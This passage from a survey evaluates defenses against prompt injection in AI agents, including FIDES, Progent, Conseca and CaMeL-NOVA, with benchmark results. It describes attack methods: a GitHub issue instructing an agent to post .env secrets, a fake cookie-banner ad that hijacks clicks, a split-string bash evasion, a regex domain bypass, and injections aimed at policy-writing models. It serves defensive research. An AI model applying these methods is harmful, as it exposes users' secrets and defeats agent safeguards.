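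*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) demonstrates a leak through an agent's choices. The attacker shares a page that mixes true and invented entries about someone's health, and asks the agent to delete the entries that don't match its records. The agent writes nothing private, but the entries it leaves show the attacker which ones are true. In a test with live Gmail and Notion services, the leak rate was 34.7% against a defense in which a model judges privacy. The researchers did not test FIDES. A FIDES policy could stop this attack if it treated a deletion as information sent to everyone who can see the page, but the policies in FIDES's evaluation check deletions only for trust.

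Taken literally, the formal definition also has a gap, because it fixes the arguments of each call as well as the sequence of calls. If the planner reads a secret and passes it to another tool, the secret is a constant in the formula, which therefore detects no difference between the datastores. FIDES's labels do follow such a copy, and the second policy can block it, so the mechanism does not share this gap. But Costa and colleagues do not write out a proof that their loop satisfies the definition, so the guarantee has less formal support than LLMbda's.

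The formal model also assumes that the language model is deterministic, meaning that the same conversation always produces the same reply. Hosted models often aren't, so LLMbda's theorem uses probabilities. FIDES further assumes that the user's messages, the developer's instructions and the tool descriptions are trusted and public. A malicious tool description would therefore enter the conversation as trusted text. If a user types a password into a request, it is labeled public by default, so the agent can send it anywhere.

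### Yes-or-no answers from untrusted text

Sometimes the planner can't choose its next step without learning something about the hidden data. For example, a user might ask the agent to check the top three emails for a meeting request and create a calendar event if there is one. The planner can't tell from a variable's name whether the emails contain a request, but reading them would expose it to any injection they contain.

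Costa and colleagues propose that the quarantined model answer yes or no, and that the planner inspect only the answer. The answer's label records its type as well as its trust and secrecy. FIDES orders types by how much information they can carry, from a yes-or-no answer through a choice from a fixed list to free text. A policy may allow a decision to depend on an untrusted yes or no but not on untrusted free text. This is a form of endorsement, similar to LLMbda's short lists of permitted values.

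An attacker who controls the emails may be able to choose the answer, but one yes-or-no answer gives them only one bit of influence. As in CaMeL's retry loop, each further answer doubles the number of combinations the attacker can choose from, so ten answers offer 1,024 and forty about 1.1 trillion. Five answers are enough to pick any letter of the alphabet, so forty could spell an eight-letter name. A planner might collect that many answers in ordinary use by asking the same question about every email in an inbox. Forty answers get the same label as one, because the join of two yes-or-no types is still a yes-or-no type. To limit the attacker's total influence, the system would also have to count the answers that the planner inspects.

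The number of bits doesn't measure the harm either, since one bit can decide whether the agent makes a payment. In the calendar example, once the planner learns that there is a request, it has the quarantined model extract the details and passes them to `set_event` in a variable. The attacker can trigger the call with one bit and fill in the date and the guests with their own text. Letting the planner see the bit is safe only if the attacker can do little harm with those details.

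The AgentDojo evaluation did not use this rule. Costa and colleagues left out constrained answers because most of the benchmark's tasks did not need them, so the results don't show whether the rule is safe or useful.

### The AgentDojo results

Costa and colleagues report that "with appropriate policies" FIDES stops every prompt injection in AgentDojo. They used a standard attack text that names the tools the attacker wants used. With GPT-4o and no policy checks, 152 injections succeeded against an ordinary planner and 21 against FIDES, whose planner could still open hidden variables and follow instructions in them. With the checks on, none succeeded against FIDES. AgentDojo's code counted three successes, but the researchers excluded them after inspecting the runs. The benchmark sometimes counts a blocked call as a success, or a harmless action that the policy permits, such as creating a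 calendar event with no guests.

For this test, the researchers labelled a data field as untrusted if at least one attack in the AgentDojo benchmark places text there. This gives the mechanism a clean test, but real developers don't know in advance which fields attackers will use. Fields without attacks could stay trusted, including the amounts of bank transactions, even though anyone who sends the user money chooses the amount. In one task, the agent has to change the user's password if it finds a suspicious transaction. GPT-4o changed it because of a large amount, without opening the untrusted descriptions, and the policy allowed the change.

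The evaluated policies were also looser than the two basic ones. The evaluated version of the first policy ignores the labels of the arguments and checks only whether the planner chose the call in a trusted conversation. The rule for `send_money` works this way. The rule for `send_email` allows any call from a trusted conversation, even if the recipient isn't permitted to read the data.

In the example of Bob's document, FIDES would keep the meeting notes in a variable, and the quarantined model would extract an address from them. The planner would then send the document without having read any untrusted text, so the evaluated policy would allow the email whether the address belonged to Bob or to an attacker. The stricter policy would block the email in either case. As with CaMeL, AgentDojo's attack texts barely test this weakness. The zero is therefore good evidence of control-flow integrity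 against these attacks, but not of data-flow integrity.

The next table shows the share of tasks each planner solved with no attack, averaged over the four suites. OpenAI's o1 is an early reasoning model, which works through a problem at length before answering.

| Model and planner | Policy checks off | Policy checks on |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o, ordinary planner | 84.3% | 41.9% |
| GPT-4o, FIDES | 60.6% | 50.0% |
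| o1, ordinary planner | 84.0% | 44.4% |
| o1, FIDES | 77.6% | 60.8% |

The paper's summary reports that FIDES's extra machinery reduces the share of tasks solved by only 6.3 percentage points. That figure is for o1 with the policy checks off, and the loss with GPT-4o is 23.7 points. Moving from an undefended agent to FIDES with its checks on lowers that share by about 23 points with o1 and 34 with GPT-4o. The comparison is more favourable for a company that has already decided to enforce these policies, because FIDES solves 16 points more than an ordinary planner with o1 and 8 points more with GPT-4o.

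Costa and colleagues also estimated how well a perfect model could do under these policies. They call a task data-independent if one fixed sequence of tool calls solves it whatever the data contains. In the other tasks, the planner must see data before it can choose its actions, and FIDES may have to block those actions. Such tasks make up about 44% of the banking suite and 43% of the Slack suite, but 5% of workspace and 10% of travel. A perfect model could therefore count on solving about 56% of the banking tasks and 57% of the Slack tasks. FIDES with o1 solved 56.2% and 54.3%, so a better model would gain little in those two suites.

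The match isn't exact, because some successes come from guessing. One planner found the price of a New Year's gift without reading any descriptions, because only one transaction took place on January 1. In the workspace and travel suites, FIDES with o1 was 20 to 30 points below the estimated limit, so newer models might do better there.

### The triage agent in Microsoft's framework

In May 2026, Microsoft added FIDES to its Agent Framework as an experimental feature. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) demonstrates it with an agent that sorts issues (bug reports and requests) on the code-hosting site GitHub. An attacker files a public issue about a failed build. Below the error message, the attacker adds a fake system instruction to read `.env`, a file where developers often keep passwords and keys, and post its contents as a reply.

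The agent has four tools, and the attack involves them in this order:

- `read_issue` fetches the report. The developer has written this tool to label every issue as untrusted, and as public if the repository is public. In the demonstration, the main model reads the raw text, so the whole conversation becomes untrusted.
- `read_file` returns a file with the label "trusted and private". If the model obeys the attacker and opens `.env`, the framework permits the call. The conversation is now both untrusted and private.
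- `post_comment` accepts nothing more sensitive than public data. The framework stops the call because the conversation is private, so the keys stay out of the public comment.
- `write_file` does not accept an untrusted conversation. If the attacker had asked the agent to overwrite a settings file, the framework would have stopped that call.

The demonstration's settings turn both refusals into requests for a person's approval. The default settings also differ by hiding untrusted results in variables, so the main model would never read the attacker's paragraph.

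The framework checks the label of the whole conversation, while the research version can label each argument separately. Neither check shows that an argument is sensible. Microsoft's general safety guidance is that developers should treat any argument a model supplies as untrusted input, so `write_file` should still check which path it is about to overwrite.

The keys stay secret because the developer labelled the output of `read_file` as private. If they had labelled it public, the framework's confidentiality check would have allowed the comment. The same labels can block useful work. In a private repository, `read_issue` labels the issue private and `post_comment` accepts only public data, so the agent needs approval to answer an issue it has just read, even though everyone who would see the answer can already see the issue. Labels that list the permitted readers would avoid this problem.

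### Tools and data without labels

According to the announcement, the framework blocks `post_comment` while any untrusted content is in the conversation, but in the code the tool limits only confidentiality. If the agent has read a malicious public issue but no private file, the conversation is untrusted but still public. The confidentiality limit would then not stop the agent from posting an attacker's link to a harmful website from the maintainer's account.

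Whether the attacker succeeds depends on how the framework treats a tool that does not declare whether it accepts untrusted content. Microsoft's documentation supports two readings. One setting lists tools that may run "even when the context is untrusted", and the example lists only `read_issue`. This suggests that undeclared tools are otherwise blocked in an untrusted context, since the list would have little purpose if they could run anyway. But in the documentation's walkthrough, `read_file` runs after the untrusted issue has entered the conversation, even though it is not on the list and declares no policy.

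The documentation never states whether a tool with no declared rule may run in an untrusted conversation. If it may, an attacker can make the agent post any public text. If it may not, the walkthrough is wrong about `read_file`, and the agent needs approval to comment on any issue it has read, which is a large part of its job. For another product, Microsoft describes a permissive policy that blocks a coding agent connected to GitHub from posting publicly only if the conversation is both untrusted and private. Developers using Agent Framework can avoid the uncertainty by declaring a rule for every tool and testing it in an untrusted conversation.

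Microsoft also gives several rules for a tool result that has no label:

| Where the rule appears | Label for unlabelled data |
|---|---|
| May 2026 announcement | Trusted and public |
| Documentation, default settings for tool results | Untrusted and public |
| Documentation, individual items of content | Trusted and public |
| Documentation, tools that declare no label | The combined label of the tool's inputs |

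In May, Microsoft asked developers whether unlabelled tools should count as untrusted by default. The settings in the documentation suggest that it has since made this change, but the other two rules are hard to reconcile with it. If an unlabelled search tool receives a query that the planner wrote from the user's request, the rule about inputs makes the search results trusted, but the default setting makes them untrusted. The framework has also changed quickly. FIDES needs version 1.3.0 or later, and Releasebot's *Agent Framework Updates & Release Notes* (2026) lists version 1.26.0 in November 2026, so developers should test the defaults in the version they use.

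The stricter default, which Microsoft describes as failing closed, does so only for trust. Failing closed means that a forgotten label leads to a refusal, not a breach. For confidentiality, three of the four rules treat unlabelled data as public, and the fourth does so if the inputs were public. If nobody labels the tool that reads the customer database, the confidentiality check will allow the agent to post customer records in a public comment.

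Assigned labels can also be wrong. Microsoft worked with GitHub to add labels to the server that connects agents to GitHub's data. According to Microsoft, the server labels files and issues from public repositories "public" and "untrusted", and those from private repositories "private" and "trusted". Outsiders can't normally write in a private repository, but an employee might paste in a customer's bug report. The server would then label the customer's text "trusted", and an agent that works only on private repositories could act on it.

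### One untrusted item and the rest of the run

Microsoft acknowledges that its way of combining labels can be too cautious. Once the text of an untrusted issue enters the conversation, everything the agent does afterwards counts as untrusted unless the developer explicitly removes the text. After sorting twenty issues, an agent needs approval to use `write_file`, even to correct a typo at the maintainer's request. Hiding untrusted results in variables avoids this only until the agent opens one of those variables.

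Microsoft is considering narrowing the scope of labels, or relaxing them when the system compacts a long conversation, which usually means replacing old messages with a shorter version. Relaxing them then would be risky because, if a model writes the shorter version after reading the attacker's text, it could repeat the attacker's instruction. Treating that version as trusted would endorse the instruction without any check.

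When the framework asks for approval, it names the tool and the label that caused the refusal. Microsoft calls these approvals coarse, because users don't see the full reasoning behind the label. A developer can find out how often refusals would interrupt an existing agent by running it with enforcement off and reading the log of calls the framework would have blocked. Neither the announcement nor the documentation reports attack or task-completion rates for the released version. The AgentDojo figures don't carry over directly, because those tests used separate labels for each argument and the labellers knew where the benchmark's attacks were.

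### Estimating what the model used

Much of this over-tainting comes from assuming that every message affects every reply. Costa and colleagues describe a method by Siddiqui and colleagues that looks for a small set of messages sufficient to produce a similar reply. The system then regenerates the reply from those messages alone and gives it only their labels. If the set excludes an irrelevant, untrusted email, the agent's next call can be trusted again.

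Generating the reply again is much safer than guessing which messages mattered, because the model no longer sees the email. But the system still has to read the email to decide what to leave out, so an attacker could in principle write text that makes it discard an important trusted message, such as an instruction never to pay a certain company. RTBAS, a related system that Costa and colleagues also describe, estimates influence from the model's internal attention or by asking another model. A wrong estimate could remove a label that should have blocked a call. FIDES uses none of these methods.

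*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) measures how well one such estimate works. Its system, NeuroTaint, examines an agent's log after the agent has finished. It first checks whether the contents of a sensitive call resemble an untrusted source in meaning, even if the wording has changed. If they don't, it removes or alters the source and estimates whether the agent would still have made the call. On 400 scenarios that the researchers built, 92.1% of the flows NeuroTaint reported were real, and it found 93.5% of the real flows. Its F1 score, which combines these two measures, was 0.928, compared with 0.522 for a baseline modelled on FIDES.

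That comparison probably understates what FIDES can block. Cai and colleagues say FIDES misses an attack in which a poisoned search result makes an agent send its research to an attacker's server. But in FIDES's basic design, the search result makes the conversation untrusted, so the policy on consequential actions blocks the call that would send the research. NeuroTaint is meant to identify what caused the call, but FIDES can block it without that information. If a designer used NeuroTaint's estimates to remove labels during a run, the 6.5% of real flows it misses would become gaps in the defense, and attackers would look for wording that produces more of them.

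FlowSeal, Shim and colleagues' defense, keeps the cautious labels but lets a second model make exceptions. Once an agent has read protected records, ordinary code intercepts every message to an unapproved recipient. The second model compares the message with the records and returns "safe" or "blocked". By the paper's theorem, nothing derived from a protected record can reach an unapproved recipient unless this model wrongly returns "safe". In tests, between 0 and 3.3% of sensitive items leaked, and the agent completed 72.4% of ordinary tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best alternative. However, the threat model excludes prompt injection. The second model has to read the outgoing message, so an attacker who can influence that message may be able to use it to give the model instructions.

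## Progent: when a model writes the policy

CaMeL and FIDES rely on policies that people write in advance, so each policy has to suit every request. An assistant needs permission to send email for some tasks, but when the user only wants a summary of the inbox, that permission mainly helps an attacker. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) has a language model write a new policy for each request and revise it while the agent works. Ordinary code still allows or blocks every tool call, but the model that writes the rules may have read an attacker's text first.

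### A policy that changes during the task

A Progent policy is a list of rules. Each rule names a tool, allows or forbids calls to it, and sets conditions on the arguments, such as a maximum value or a text pattern. It also determines what happens after a refusal: the agent can stop, ask the user, or receive an error message and try something else. A rule for the messaging service Slack might look like this, slightly simplified:

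`allow send_slack_msg when { to == "alice" }, fallback "Try another way"`

Progent checks each tool call against the forbidding rules first and the allowing rules second, and blocks any call that matches neither. It checks only the tool's name and the values of the arguments. It doesn't record where a value came from, so a rule that allows messages to Alice allows any message to her, including one whose text an attacker supplied.

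In the paper's main example, a user asks the agent to carry out the actions in an email from Alice with the subject "TODOs for the week". For a request like this, CaMeL's planner wrote a program containing every tool. Progent instead starts with a small policy and changes it as the agent learns more.

| What the policy model has seen | Policy it writes | Type of change |
|---|---|---|
| The request | Allow a search for Alice's email with that subject | Initial policy |
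| Alice's list, which asks for a summary of recent emails on Slack | Also allow reading 20 emails, looking up the user's Slack name and sending Slack messages | Expansion |
| The user's Slack name, `alice` | Allow Slack messages only to `alice` | Narrowing |
| The 20 emails, one with an injection to forward the inbox to an outsider | No change, or also allow `send_email` if the injection works | None, or expansion |

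Progent applies a policy change automatically if it is a narrowing but requires approval if it is an expansion. A change is a narrowing if the old policy already allowed every tool call that the new one allows. Any other change is an expansion, even if it also removes some permissions. To check, Progent uses an SMT solver, a program that determines whether any values can satisfy a set of logical conditions. For each tool, the solver looks for arguments that the new rules allow and the old rules do not.

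Shi and colleagues call the resulting guarantee monotonic confinement, meaning that between approvals the set of permitted calls can only shrink or stay the same. The guarantee covers changes to the policy but not the initial policy, which also comes from a model. If the initial policy lets `send_money` pay anyone, later policies can keep that permission without approval.

### Where an attacker's text reaches the policy

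Progent assumes that the user's request is benign. Under that assumption, the initial policy is safe from injection because the model writes it from only the request and the tool descriptions. After each tool call, Progent queries the policy model to check whether the call might require a policy update. This query includes the call but not its result. If the model outputs yes, a second query includes the result and requests a new policy. An attacker's text can reach the policy through this second query.

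*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that a malicious tool result could make this update relax the constraints. The solver would classify that change as an expansion, but it would classify the change that Alice's to-do list requires the same way, so someone or something still has to decide which expansion to accept. In the example of Bob's document, the policy model would read the meeting notes and propose a rule that allows email to the address in them. The proposal would look just as reasonable if an attacker had changed the address.

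An attacker can also exploit an update that narrows the policy. Suppose the current policy allows Slack messages to anyone, and a tool result contains a false name for the recipient. The policy model might then allow messages only to the attacker's account, and Progent would apply the change automatically. The attacker gains no new permission, since the old policy already allowed messages to that account, but the new policy blocks messages to the correct recipient.

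*Contextual Agent Security* (Tsai and Bagdasarian, 2025) describes Conseca, a system built at Google that avoids this exposure. Its policy model receives only the request, the tool documentation and context that the developer has marked as trusted. The model writes the policy once per task and gives a reason for each rule, which a person can review. Ordinary code enforces the policy. For a request to answer urgent work emails, the policy forbids `delete_email` and allows `send_email` only if the sender is Alice, the recipient has a work address and the subject contains "urgent".

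The rules in Conseca's prototype are regular expressions (patterns for matching text), and small mistakes in them can have serious effects. If a pattern for addresses at `work.com` doesn't mark the end of the address, it can also match `eve@work.com.evil.com`. The policy also depends on which context the developer chooses to trust. The prototype trusts the names of files and folders, so if the agent had saved an attachment under a name the sender chose, that name could contain an instruction to the policy model.

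Conseca's policy model also can't predict actions that depend on data it hasn't seen. Tsai and Bagdasarian give the example of carrying out the tasks in a manager's email. In a small trial of 20 tasks, their agent completed an average of 12.0 with Conseca and 14.0 with no policy. They also planted an email asking for messages about security vulnerabilities to be forwarded. Conseca blocked the forwarding in every task except one, in which the user had asked the agent to perform the tasks in urgent emails. That request was broad enough that the policy model wrote a policy allowing the forwarding, even though the model had seen no untrusted text.

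### The published results and their settings

With GPT-4o as both agent and policy writer, Progent reduced the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%. On Agent Security Bench (ASB), which covers ten kinds of agent, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Shi and colleagues report little change in the share of tasks solved.

Progent reports these results with every expansion approved automatically, to simulate a careless user. This is a demanding test of the policy model, but it also means monotonic confinement did not contribute to the headline figures, because the set of permitted calls could grow at any time. The figures measure how well GPT-4o wrote and revised policies while exposed to the benchmark's injections.

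Most of the protection on AgentDojo came from the initial policy. The attack success rate fell to 2.5% without any updates, and updates lowered it by only another 1.5 percentage points. Rejecting every expansion gave a slightly lower attack success rate than approving them all. With a human reviewer the rate was zero, but Shi and colleagues assumed a reviewer who would reject malicious addresses and never allow unrestricted payments, so that result shows only what good review could achieve.

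The AgentDojo tests also used a hand-written rule that allowed harmless read-only tools for every task. The ASB tests had no such rule, and most of the remaining attacks there used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate tools. Hand-written rules based on knowledge of which tools to trust stopped these attacks. The policy model lacked that knowledge, and Shi and colleagues doubt that a person without it would have done better.

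They also tried three attacks tailored to Progent's design, again with every expansion approved. One told any model updating the policy to allow all tools. Another added a reminder to permit whatever the injected task needed. The third used AgentVigil, an automated system that searches for effective injections. None raised the attack success rate by much, and Narisetty and colleagues put the rates at roughly 0.5% to 4.2%.

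### A reproduction with a small open model

Narisetty and colleagues repeated this kind of test in 2026 with Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, on a single graphics processor. The model served as both the agent and the policy writer. They used the first eight user tasks in each of three AgentDojo suites, paired each task with every injection task in its suite, and ran the study three times. They left out the travel suite because the model got stuck in very long loops.

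The study compared an undefended agent, Progent under AgentDojo's standard attack, and Progent under an attack aimed at the model that writes the policy. The last attack described the malicious action as a routine step the user had already authorised, so that the model would add a rule allowing it. The published percentages imply the following numbers of successful attacks.

| Suite | Attacked runs per condition | No defense, standard attack | Progent, standard attack | Progent, attack on the policy writer |
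|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 216 | 41 (19.0%) | 4 (1.9%) | 8 (3.7%) |
| Slack | 120 | 70 (58.3%) | 13 (10.8%) | 5 (4.2%) |
| Workspace | 144 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Average of the suites | | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |

Progent reduced successful attacks to about a sixth, but the agent also completed far fewer user tasks. Under attack, it completed 45.2% of them without Progent, 27.1% with it, and 25.8% under the attack on the policy writer. The loss was concentrated in the Slack and workspace suites, where the completion rate fell by around half. Writing and updating the policies also raised the number of model calls per task to about 15 times what it was without Progent.

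The 2.6% is not evidence that Progent becomes safer when an attacker targets it. The injected text has to persuade both the agent to request the action and the policy model to allow it. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that the milder wording meant for the policy model made the agent less likely to comply. They did not run the new attack against an undefended agent, which would have shown how persuasive it was. If it rarely worked there either, the low figure would be weak evidence about Progent.

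Only the Slack and banking suites had successful attacks, which fell from 13 to 5 in Slack but rose from 4 to 8 in banking. Both changes involve few cases. The three runs gave similar results, but they repeated the same tasks with the model's randomness set to zero, so they show that the experiment is reproducible without showing that the result would hold for other tasks.

The researchers work at LaunchSafe, which sells agent security and builds its tools on the same approach, so a favourable result helps its business. They are still frank in their paper about the test's limits, and they propose next trying an attack that uses only permitted actions.

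### Fixed tests and attackers who adapt

AgentDojo's standard attack is a fixed text written before Progent existed, whereas real attackers can study a defense, try many versions of an attack and keep the ones that come closest to working.

This difference has misled researchers before. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) tested twelve defenses that work through prompts, training or filters. Some were meant to stop prompt injection and others to stop jailbreaks, in which users try to get forbidden answers from a model. The original papers reported attack success rates near zero for most of these defenses, but attacks designed for each one succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the twelve.

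Spotlighting marks certain text with special delimiters, and prompt sandwiching repeats the user's request after the untrusted text. AgentDojo's fixed attacks had success rates as low as 1% against these defenses. Nasr and colleagues then used a search in which a language model proposed changes to the injected text and a program kept the most successful versions. This search succeeded more than 95% of the time against both defenses. One successful text presented the attacker's actions as a security check that the agent had to complete before the user's task. Repeating the user's request did not help, because the agent treated the check as part of that request.

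Narisetty and colleagues used a similar disguise to attack Progent's policy writer, but they wrote a single version by hand and did not refine it. AgentVigil is closer to a real search, though Shi and colleagues ran it only as one test of their own system. Both attacks involved less effort than the ones that defeated the twelve earlier defenses.

Progent should be harder to defeat, because no wording can make the rule checker accept a call that the policy forbids. An attacker needs a bad policy, an approved expansion of it, or a way to do harm with calls it already allows. The last may not require deceiving the policy model. In the to-do list example, the policy allows Slack messages to `alice` with any content, so an attacker who influences the summary can send the user a malicious link. Attacks that stay within the permissions a task needs are outside Progent's scope, and these tests did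 not search for them systematically.

### Tasks that change along the way

AgentDojo also makes writing policies unusually easy. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) reports that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 user tasks require an agent to change its plan because of something it finds. This helps explain why Progent's initial policies did so well, and perhaps why Shi and colleagues found that only 6% of policy updates were expansions.

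AgentDyn is a benchmark of 60 tasks involving shopping, GitHub and daily life, all of which require the agent to adjust its plan. Each task includes a legitimate instruction in outside data, such as a request to log in before paying, so an agent can't succeed by ignoring all instructions in that data. The tasks average 7.1 steps and 33 available tools, compared with about 3.5 steps and 20 tools in AgentDojo. Li and colleagues ran Progent on AgentDyn with four models.

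| Model | Tasks solved, no defense | Tasks solved, Progent | Attack success, no defense | Attack success, Progent |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 32 of 60 | 4 of 60 | 37.80% | 1.69% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 31 of 60 | 15 of 60 | 20.61% | 1.59% |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 36 of 60 | 8 of 60 | 11.89% | 0.00% |
| Llama 3.3 70B | 6 of 60 | 2 of 60 | 11.91% | 0.52% |

The task counts are for runs without an attack. Under attack, GPT-4o's completion rate fell from 55.52% to 5.83% when Li and colleagues added Progent. They found that the policy model could not reliably set accurate permissions for so many tools, and its mistakes accumulated until the policy blocked almost every useful tool. The attack success rates are therefore hard to credit to good policies, since an agent with so few useful tools can do little for an attacker.

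CaMeL solved none of the tasks with any of the four models, and no attack on it succeeded. Its fixed plan can't include actions that become necessary only after the agent has read something. Progent is designed to allow such actions, but on these tasks the policy model was rarely good enough to do so. The attacks were fixed texts here too, so the benchmark tests usefulness better than it tests security.

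### When every action is a shell command

Progent's rules work best when each tool has a narrow purpose and clearly named arguments. Many coding agents instead use a shell, a single tool that can read files, install software and contact other computers. *INFUSE* (Nguyen, Guo and colleagues, 2026) tested this setting with agents that could issue one shell command per turn.

The tests used adaptations of Progent and CaMeL, not the original systems. The Progent adaptation broke each command into its basic operations and checked these against a list of permitted operations derived from the user's task. The CaMeL adaptation kept the idea of a data-flow policy fixed in advance, but not the interpreter or the quarantined model. Each adaptation was tested on 200 combinations of task and attack with each of five models.

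| Model | Attack success, no defense | Attack success, Progent adaptation | Attack success, CaMeL adaptation | Tasks completed, no defense | Tasks completed, Progent adaptation |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-14B | 27.3% | 35.0% | 31.5% | 48.5% | 43.5% |
| Gemma 3 12B | 32.7% | 30.5% | 31.9% | 23.6% | 6.0% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 46.5% | 43.0% | 43.0% | 54.0% | 17.0% |
| Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite | 55.5% | 63.5% | 55.2% | 71.5% | 25.5% |
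| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 6.5% | 27.1% | 9.2% | Not recorded | Not recorded |

Neither adaptation measurably reduced attack success with any model. The only clear change was the increase for Claude with the Progent adaptation. That comparison is hard to interpret because, in the main benchmark, a spending limit had cut Claude's runs short and lowered its attack success rate. Nguyen and colleagues say their conclusions do not apply to every version of Progent or CaMeL.

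The scoring method may also have hidden some of the benefit. A language model judged each run and was told to count an agent as compromised if it adopted the attacker's goal, even partially. If an agent decided to upload a secret key and the defense blocked the command, the judge could still count the attack as successful. The benchmark also has a measure based on changes to files and systems, but the published comparison of these two defenses doesn't use it. The loss of completed tasks is easier to interpret, and it resembles what Li and colleagues found with the original Progent.

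*Beyond Handcrafted Security* (2026) shows how a rule for shell commands can fail. Its system, HARD, has a model write new rules after seeing attacks. In one test, an attacker stored "ba" and "sh" in two variables over several turns, then combined them to run `bash`. None of the 18 rules in force matched, because they checked only the command's text, which never contained the word "bash". When the same system used written guidance for the agent instead of rules in code, the agent recognised the trick and refused, although such guidance can fail against a more persuasive attacker.

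### Correct enforcement of a mistaken rule

Failures of this kind come from the rule, since the program applied it exactly as written. *Only What You've Signed up For* (Cardei, Pinto and colleagues, 2026) tests enforcement and policy writing separately. Its system, CoDA, uses diffusion language models, which produce a rough version of a whole passage and refine it in steps. At each step, CoDA restricts the tool names and sensitive arguments to values the policy permits. No attacks succeeded when the researchers supplied correct policies. When a model chose the policies, the result depended on whether it chose correctly.

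Shi and colleagues' AgentDojo results don't separate the two. Their 1.0% reflects how often GPT-4o's policies and the agent's behaviour together allowed one of the benchmark's attacks. The rate varies with the policy model, though it stayed below 5% with every model they tried. AgentDyn shows that a larger set of tools can ruin the policies even without an attacker. The proof of monotonic confinement holds in each case, because it does not cover whether the policy suits the task.

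Protecting the policy writer from injected instructions doesn't fully solve this problem either. *Poisoning Self-Evolving Security Policies in LLM Agents* (2026) describes attacks on SED, a defense that learns rules from past incidents. Attempts to insert instructions into its policies failed, and its judge was right in all 10 cases designed to fool it. The attack that worked gave SED a real harmful incident to learn from. SED recognised the harm but wrote too broad a rule.

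A person who finds a mistake in a hand-written policy can correct it for every later request. Progent's model writes a new policy for each task, so a mistake may affect only one task, but correcting it doesn't prevent a similar mistake in the next. Developers can add permanent rules that the model's policies can't override, such as a ban on payments to unknown accounts, but then they must decide in advance which legitimate payments to block, as they would with a hand-written policy.

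## Computer-use agents: steering a fixed plan with false observations

Progent and the systems before it control tools that have names and labelled arguments. Computer-use agents look at screenshots and operate ordinary programs and websites by clicking, typing and scrolling. They can work where nobody has built a tool for the job. But the dual-model design relies on actions with a known meaning and on plans that a planner can write without looking at anything, and computer-use agents lack both.

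### A click has no fixed meaning

*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard et al., 2026) compares `send_email(to, subject, body)` with `click(x, y)`. `send_email` always sends an email, so a policy can check the recipient. `click` might log in, delete data or open a malicious website, depending on what is at that point on the screen, but a policy can check only the two coordinates.

Rules about navigation are also easy to get around. *ceLLMate* (Meng, Feng and colleagues, 2025) describes an attack on Operator, OpenAI's browser agent. A public GitHub issue contained instructions to copy the user's private email address from their Hacker News account and send it to the attacker. When Meng and colleagues tried the obvious defense on another browser agent, forbidding it to go to Hacker News, it searched for the site on DuckDuckGo and clicked the result.

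Planning is also harder for an isolated planner. An ordinary computer-use agent takes a new screenshot after every action and uses it to choose the next one. An isolated planner gets no screenshots, so it has to write a branch in advance for each possibility, such as whether a browser is open, whether a pop-up covers the page and where the search box is.

### Observe, verify, act

Foerster and colleagues built CaMeL-NOVA, which keeps CaMeL's planner and interpreter and uses a vision model as the quarantined model. The planner's instructions tell it to build each step from three parts. First the quarantined model describes the screen. Then a function compares the description with the state that the plan expects. If they match, the quarantined model locates the right button or field, and the interpreter clicks it. In outline, a routine for cookie banners looks like this:

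```
screen = summarize_screenshot("Describe any pop-up on the page")
if verify_hypothesis(screen, "A cookie banner is visible"):
    button = find("the button that accepts cookies")
    click(button)
```

Plans of this kind are much longer than CaMeL's plans for AgentDojo. The table compares them on OSWorld, a benchmark of 369 tasks in programs such as Chrome, LibreOffice and the image editor GIMP.

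| Average per plan | CaMeL, AgentDojo | CaMeL without the three-part method, OSWorld | CaMeL-NOVA, OSWorld |
|---|---|---|---|
| Lines of code | 51.8 | 71.6 | 213.3 |
| Tool calls | 4.9 | 19.8 | 41.1 |
| Branches | 3.7 | 11.3 | 39.7 |
| Branches that depend on a quarantined model's answer | 1.9 | 7.9 | 24.2 |

Roughly half of a CaMeL-NOVA plan consists of fallbacks that don't run, but they are still worth having. Within three attempts, CaMeL solved 11 of 60 tasks without the method and 35 with it. UI-TARS, a small open vision model, had solved all 60 on its own. The last row of the table matters most for security, because each of those branches gives an attacker a chance to influence the agent by deceiving the quarantined model.

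The paper reports that CaMeL-NOVA improves the performance of small open models by up to 19%. That figure comes from UI-TARS, which solved 29.0% of tasks with CaMeL-NOVA and 24.4% alone. But UI-TARS had three attempts at each task with CaMeL-NOVA and only one alone. On the first attempt, it solved 51 tasks with CaMeL-NOVA and 60 alone, out of the 339 that OSWorld can score automatically.

The paper also reports that the design retains up to 57% of the performance of larger models. Of 109 tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 solved alone, CaMeL-NOVA solved 62 within five attempts and 31 on the first. Retrying is harmless on a benchmark that resets each time, but on a real computer a failed plan may already have changed something.

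Foerster and colleagues adapted FIDES in the same way. The adapted version solved about as many tasks but used 29.6 times as many tokens as an undefended agent, because its planner rereads the whole history at every step. CaMeL-NOVA used 1.88 times as many. The FIDES planner can see yes-or-no answers about the screen, but limits on the number of calls in a run and on how often it can reuse one variable restrict how much an attacker can tell it through those answers.

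### Steering a plan without changing it

Branch steering can make a CaMeL program pay a disputed bill, and it can work in more ways when the program operates a computer screen. A false report from the quarantined model can send the program down a harmful branch that the plan permits, or make it click the wrong spot.

The cookie routine is an easy target because almost every plan for a web task contains one. Suppose an attacker buys an advertisement that looks like a cookie banner. The quarantined model reports that a banner is visible and returns a location inside the advertisement. The interpreter clicks there, and the browser opens the attacker's website, even though the program runs exactly as the planner wrote it. The trick also works on pages the agent visits later, because each `find` call uses only the current screen.

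Piet, Chow and colleagues (2026) conclude in *Web Agents Should Adopt the Compile-and-Execute Paradigm* that fixing a program does not determine what its clicks do. Control-flow integrity therefore guarantees less here than it did for CaMeL, because a program that contains a click could do anything a click on that screen can do.

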